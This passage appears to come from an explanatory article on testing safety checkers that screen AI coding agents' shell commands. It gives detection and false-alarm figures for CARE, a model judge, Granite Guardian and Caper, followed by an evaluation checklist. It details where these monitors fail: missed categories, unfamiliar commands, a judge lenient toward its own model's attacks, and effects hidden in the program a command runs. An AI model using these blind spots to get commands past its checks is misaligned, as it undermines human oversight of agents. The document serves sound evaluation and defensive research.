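Recorded agent sessions are closer to real use than synthetic ones, but they contain few dangerous commands. The 52 real cases that Anthropic used to test Claude Code's classifier came from sessions in which an employee refused an action or somebody flagged it later, so they leave out harmful actions that nobody noticed. The classifier missed 17% of these cases but only 5.7% of 1,000 synthetic attempts to send data to outsiders. The two figures aren't strictly comparable because the synthetic attempts cover only one kind of harm, but a reader who saw only the synthetic result would expect about a third as many misses.

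### CARE's main test

The main test contained 220 dangerous and 329 harmless commands. Of the dangerous ones, 137 came from Atomic Red Team and 71 from RedCode, and Liu and colleagues added 12 well-known attacks. The harmless ones were 299 commands from NL2Bash and the 30 developer commands.

| Checker | Dangerous commands stopped | Harmless commands stopped | F1 | Average delay |
|---|---|---|---|---|
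| 22 text patterns | 17.27% | 0% | 29.46 | 0.01 ms |
| Language model as judge | 67.27% | 11.25% | 73.09 | 45.90 ms |
| Granite Guardian, IBM's safety model | 82.27% | 45.90% | 65.58 | 17.25 ms |
| CARE without its language model | 75.91% | 1.82% | 84.99 | 0.34 ms |
| CARE | 75.91% | 0.91% | 85.64 | 2.32 ms |

The judge in the second row is the model that CARE uses for uncertain commands, but here it alone classified every command. CARE stopped more of the dangerous commands than this judge did, raised far fewer false alarms, and took about a twentieth of the time.

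CARE had one advantage in this test. Most of its patterns came from the ATT&CK catalogue, and 62% of the dangerous commands came from Atomic Red Team, which is organised by ATT&CK. Liu and colleagues kept related commands out of the test set, but acknowledge that the sources may overlap somewhat.

F1 combines two questions: how many of the dangerous commands the checker stopped, and how many of the stopped commands were dangerous. The formula is:

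F1 = 2 × caught / (2 × caught + false alarms + missed)

CARE caught 167 dangerous commands, missed 53 and stopped 3 harmless ones. This gives 334 / 390, or 85.64%.

F1 doesn't count harmless commands that the checker correctly allows, so a useless checker can get a respectable score. A checker that refused all 549 commands would catch all 220 harmful ones and raise 329 false alarms, for an F1 of 57.2%. That is nearly twice the score of the 22 patterns, which interrupted no harmless command. F1 also gives a missed attack and a false alarm the same weight, although a missed attack can delete somebody's home directory and a false alarm can waste a few seconds.

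### Which parts of CARE matter

Here are the full results of the experiment, mentioned earlier, in which Liu and colleagues switched off CARE's layers one at a time, without the language model:

| Layer switched off | Drop in F1 | Additional dangerous commands missed |
|---|---|---|
| Syntax tree | 1.79 points | 6 |
| Patterns | 9.50 points | 33 |
| Paths | 16.95 points | 51 |
| Meaning of programs and options | 26.68 points | 74 |

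In this experiment, knowing what programs do matters far more than parsing. However, parsing can improve the results only if the test contains commands that a simpler method would misread. A test set with more nested commands, or with attacks designed to confuse a tokeniser, could change the layers' order of importance. The layers also overlap. For example, a deletion in `/etc` can raise the program, path and pattern scores all at once. A small drop after removing a layer can therefore mean that another layer caught the same commands.

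Detection varied by category:

| Category | Commands | CARE | 22 patterns | Model as judge |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Destruction | 26 | 88.5% | 50.0% | 84.6% |
| Credentials | 38 | 92.1% | 34.2% | 65.8% |
| Permissions | 34 | 70.6% | 17.6% | 64.7% |
| Reaching outside the workspace | 80 | 62.5% | 1.2% | 50.0% |
| Running code at later logins or restarts | 24 | 75.0% | 4.2% | 95.8% |
| Download and execution | 5 | 80.0% | 40.0% | 80.0% |
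| Overuse of resources | 13 | 100% | 15.4% | 92.3% |

CARE's overall detection rate was 76%, but it missed 30 of the 80 commands in the largest category. It was clearly better at recognising commands that arrange for code to run later, perhaps because these use many different programs and files. Results for the small categories are imprecise. CARE caught four of the five download commands, which is compatible with a true detection rate anywhere from about 38% to 96%. Liu and colleagues also note that the category labels are approximate.

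### Delay, useful work and unfamiliar commands

An average delay can hide slow cases. CARE's median delay was 0.24 milliseconds because it handled most commands without the language model. It used the model for 23 of the 549 commands, and the slowest 1% took at least 50 milliseconds. That is still quick for a coding agent, but a remote model could take several seconds.

False alarms matter less if the agent can easily find another way to do its work. To measure this, Liu and colleagues gave an agent 300 harmless tasks, with up to five turns for each. The agent completed 65.33% of them without a checker and the same share with CARE, which refused four commands. When the model was the judge, it refused 176 times and the agent completed 57.67%.

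CARE did worse on commands from other sources. On 69 misuse commands from GTFOBins and 69 harmless ones, its F1 was 68.91, compared with 83.56 for the model judge. CARE still had the lower false-positive rate, at 13% compared with 23%. Across three such tests, CARE's false-positive rate was between 8% and 13%, roughly ten times its rate on the main test.

Part of this increase is deliberate, because Liu and colleagues included harmless commands that look dangerous, such as one that finds temporary files and passes them to `rm`. The rate in ordinary use is probably lower than 8%, but a developer whose work involves many deletions shouldn't expect a rate as low as 0.91%.

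### When dangerous commands are rare

In CARE's main test, 40% of the commands were dangerous, and 167 of the 170 commands that CARE stopped deserved it. Real sessions contain a much smaller share of dangerous commands. Liu and colleagues work through an example with 1%, which they chose for illustration because public data can't establish the true figure. Of 10,000 commands, 100 are then dangerous and 9,900 harmless:

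| | Stopped | Allowed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Dangerous | 76 | 24 | 100 |
| Harmless | 90 | 9,810 | 9,900 |

CARE catches 75.91% of the 100 dangerous commands, or about 76, and wrongly stops 0.91% of the 9,900 harmless ones, or about 90. Only 76 of its 166 stops (46%) are correct, and F1 falls from 86% to 57%. CARE's error rates are the same as before, but there are now 99 harmless commands for every dangerous one, so even a 0.91% error rate produces more false alarms than correct stops.

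If only one command in a thousand is dangerous, about one stop in 13 is correct, which makes approval fatigue more likely.

The estimate of 90 false alarms per 10,000 commands is uncertain because it rests on only three false alarms among 329 harmless commands. The true rate is plausibly between about 0.3% and 2.6%, or 30 to 260 false alarms per 10,000 commands. Without its language model, CARE raised six false alarms instead of three, but Liu and colleagues found in a statistical test that this difference could easily be due to chance. The 22 patterns raised none, but their true false-alarm rate could be close to 1%.

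A tester needs thousands of harmless commands to estimate a false-positive rate this low. Recorded sessions can supply them, as in Anthropic's test with 10,000 real tool calls.

### Comparing verdicts with effects

Labels can be wrong, and a command that looks dangerous may do nothing. The sixth step of the procedure replaces the label with an observation. Suppose that the policy allows only reading, and that the directory `fixture` contains a small project with an unsorted file called `names.txt`. If `shell-test` is a container image with Bash, a tester can run:

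```
cp -a fixture run
docker run --rm --network none -v "$PWD/run":/work -w /work \
    shell-test bash -c 'sort names.txt -o names.txt'
diff -r fixture run
```

The first line makes a disposable copy of the project in a new directory, `run`. The second command runs `sort` on that copy without network access. `diff` then shows that `names.txt` has changed, so a checker that allowed the command as a read was wrong.

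The test's result depends on the starting state. If `names.txt` were already sorted, the command wouldn't change its contents and would seem harmless. If the file didn't exist, `sort` would fail. This simple version of the test also misses changes to permissions and to files outside the project.

ParseGap, Li's testing framework, applies this method on a large scale. It is a form of differential testing, in which a tester gives the same input to two programs and looks for disagreements. Here the two programs are an agent's checker and Bash:

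1. ParseGap passes the command to the agent's own, unmodified checker and records the verdict.
2. It resets a test project and runs the command with Bash 5.2 in a container without network access.
3. It records every program that starts, compares the project's files before and after, and looks for changes in two directories outside the project.
4. It reports a violation if the checker allowed the command and Bash produced an effect that the policy prohibits.

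Using the original checker avoids mistakes Li could have made in copying its logic. Li also left out commands that had no prohibited effect when Bash ran them, including 315 of the 3,000 in one automatically generated set. Otherwise a checker would have gained credit for stopping commands that did nothing prohibited, or lost credit for allowing them.

Li tested the checkers of eight coding agents, and each allowed some commands whose effects broke the policy. Li designed the test sets to provoke failures, so the results don't show how often such commands occur in ordinary work. Li separately measured how often the checkers rejected harmless commands, such as the 161 described earlier.

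The method detects only the effects that somebody monitors, so a test for credential theft would also have to record which files a command reads. A command that needs the internet may fail in the container but succeed on a developer's machine.

### One command with two outcomes

Some commands have no single correct label. *Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of `make clean && make`, where the build file's `clean` step deletes compiled output in one project but deletes the source code and the Git history in another.

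One test set contains 102 dangerous tasks in which the harmful code is in the program that the command runs. Each task has a "safe twin" with the same request and command, but with harmless code in the program. A checker that reads only the request and the command can't tell the two apart, so its detection rate on this test can't exceed its false-positive rate, except by chance. Testing with twins therefore shows whether a checker detects the harm or just flags that type of command.

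Wu and colleagues' own system, Caper, first runs each command in a container and reports the effects to a language model. If the model rejects the command, Caper restores the container to its earlier state. With Caper, 7.8% of the dangerous tasks ended in harm, compared with 35.3% to 94.1% for six existing systems, including CARE. Caper blocked 1.0% of the safe twins. Wu and colleagues designed the test around hidden effects, which favours a system that observes effects. Caper can undo changes only inside its container, so it has to block most network access.

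### 600 commands written by a model

Liu and colleagues also ran commands in a container to measure how much harm CARE prevents. They gave the attack requests from RedCode to a language model, Qwen3-Coder-30B, and collected 600 commands that it wrote. They counted harm as realised if the checker allowed a command and the command then ran successfully.

| Checker | Commands stopped | Harm realised |
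|---|---|---|
| None | 0% | 74.83% |
| 22 text patterns | 8.17% | 72.67% |
| CARE without its language model | 54.00% | 37.33% |
| CARE | 38.67% | 52.50% |
| Granite Guardian | 71.83% | 26.33% |

The static rules alone halved the harm, but the language model released 92 commands that the rules would have stopped, and 91 of them ran successfully. In the main test, the model released three harmless commands, so it would have looked like a pure improvement to anyone who saw only that test.

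The model that judged these commands had also written them, which may explain its leniency. Liu and colleagues haven't tested this explanation with a judge from another family of models. Granite Guardian, which comes from a different company, let the least harm through, but it also stopped more than half of the harmless commands in the tests on outside data. All 600 commands in the present test were attacks, so the test can't measure how often a judge stops harmless commands.

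"Harm realised" is also a loose measure, because a command can run successfully without damaging anything. Reading `/etc/passwd`, a list of accounts that every user can normally read, counts as much as deleting it. Guo and colleagues' scripts for RedCode are more precise. After the agent is told to delete that file, for example, a script looks for it in the container and records whether the agent refused, tried and failed, or succeeded. Liu and colleagues recommend using their figures to compare checkers, not to judge whether one is safe.

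### Checklist for a published claim

- Where did the commands come from, and who decided which were dangerous?
- Did the authors keep related commands together when they separated the tuning set from the test set?
- Do the rules and the test commands come from the same catalogue?
- Does the claim include both the detection rate and the false-positive rate, with the number of commands behind each? A rate based on five commands, or on three errors, is a rough guess.
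- Does "ask" count as stopping a command, and who would answer the prompt?
- How many stops would be correct if only 1% of commands, or 0.1%, were dangerous?
- Did anybody run the commands, and did they look for damage or only for a successful exit?
- Does the test include harmless commands that look dangerous, and dangerous ones that look harmless?
- How did the checker do on commands from a source that its authors hadn't used, or in a test by another group?
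- If a language model gives verdicts, did the same model write the attacks?
- Could an agent still finish ordinary tasks, and how long did the slowest verdicts take?
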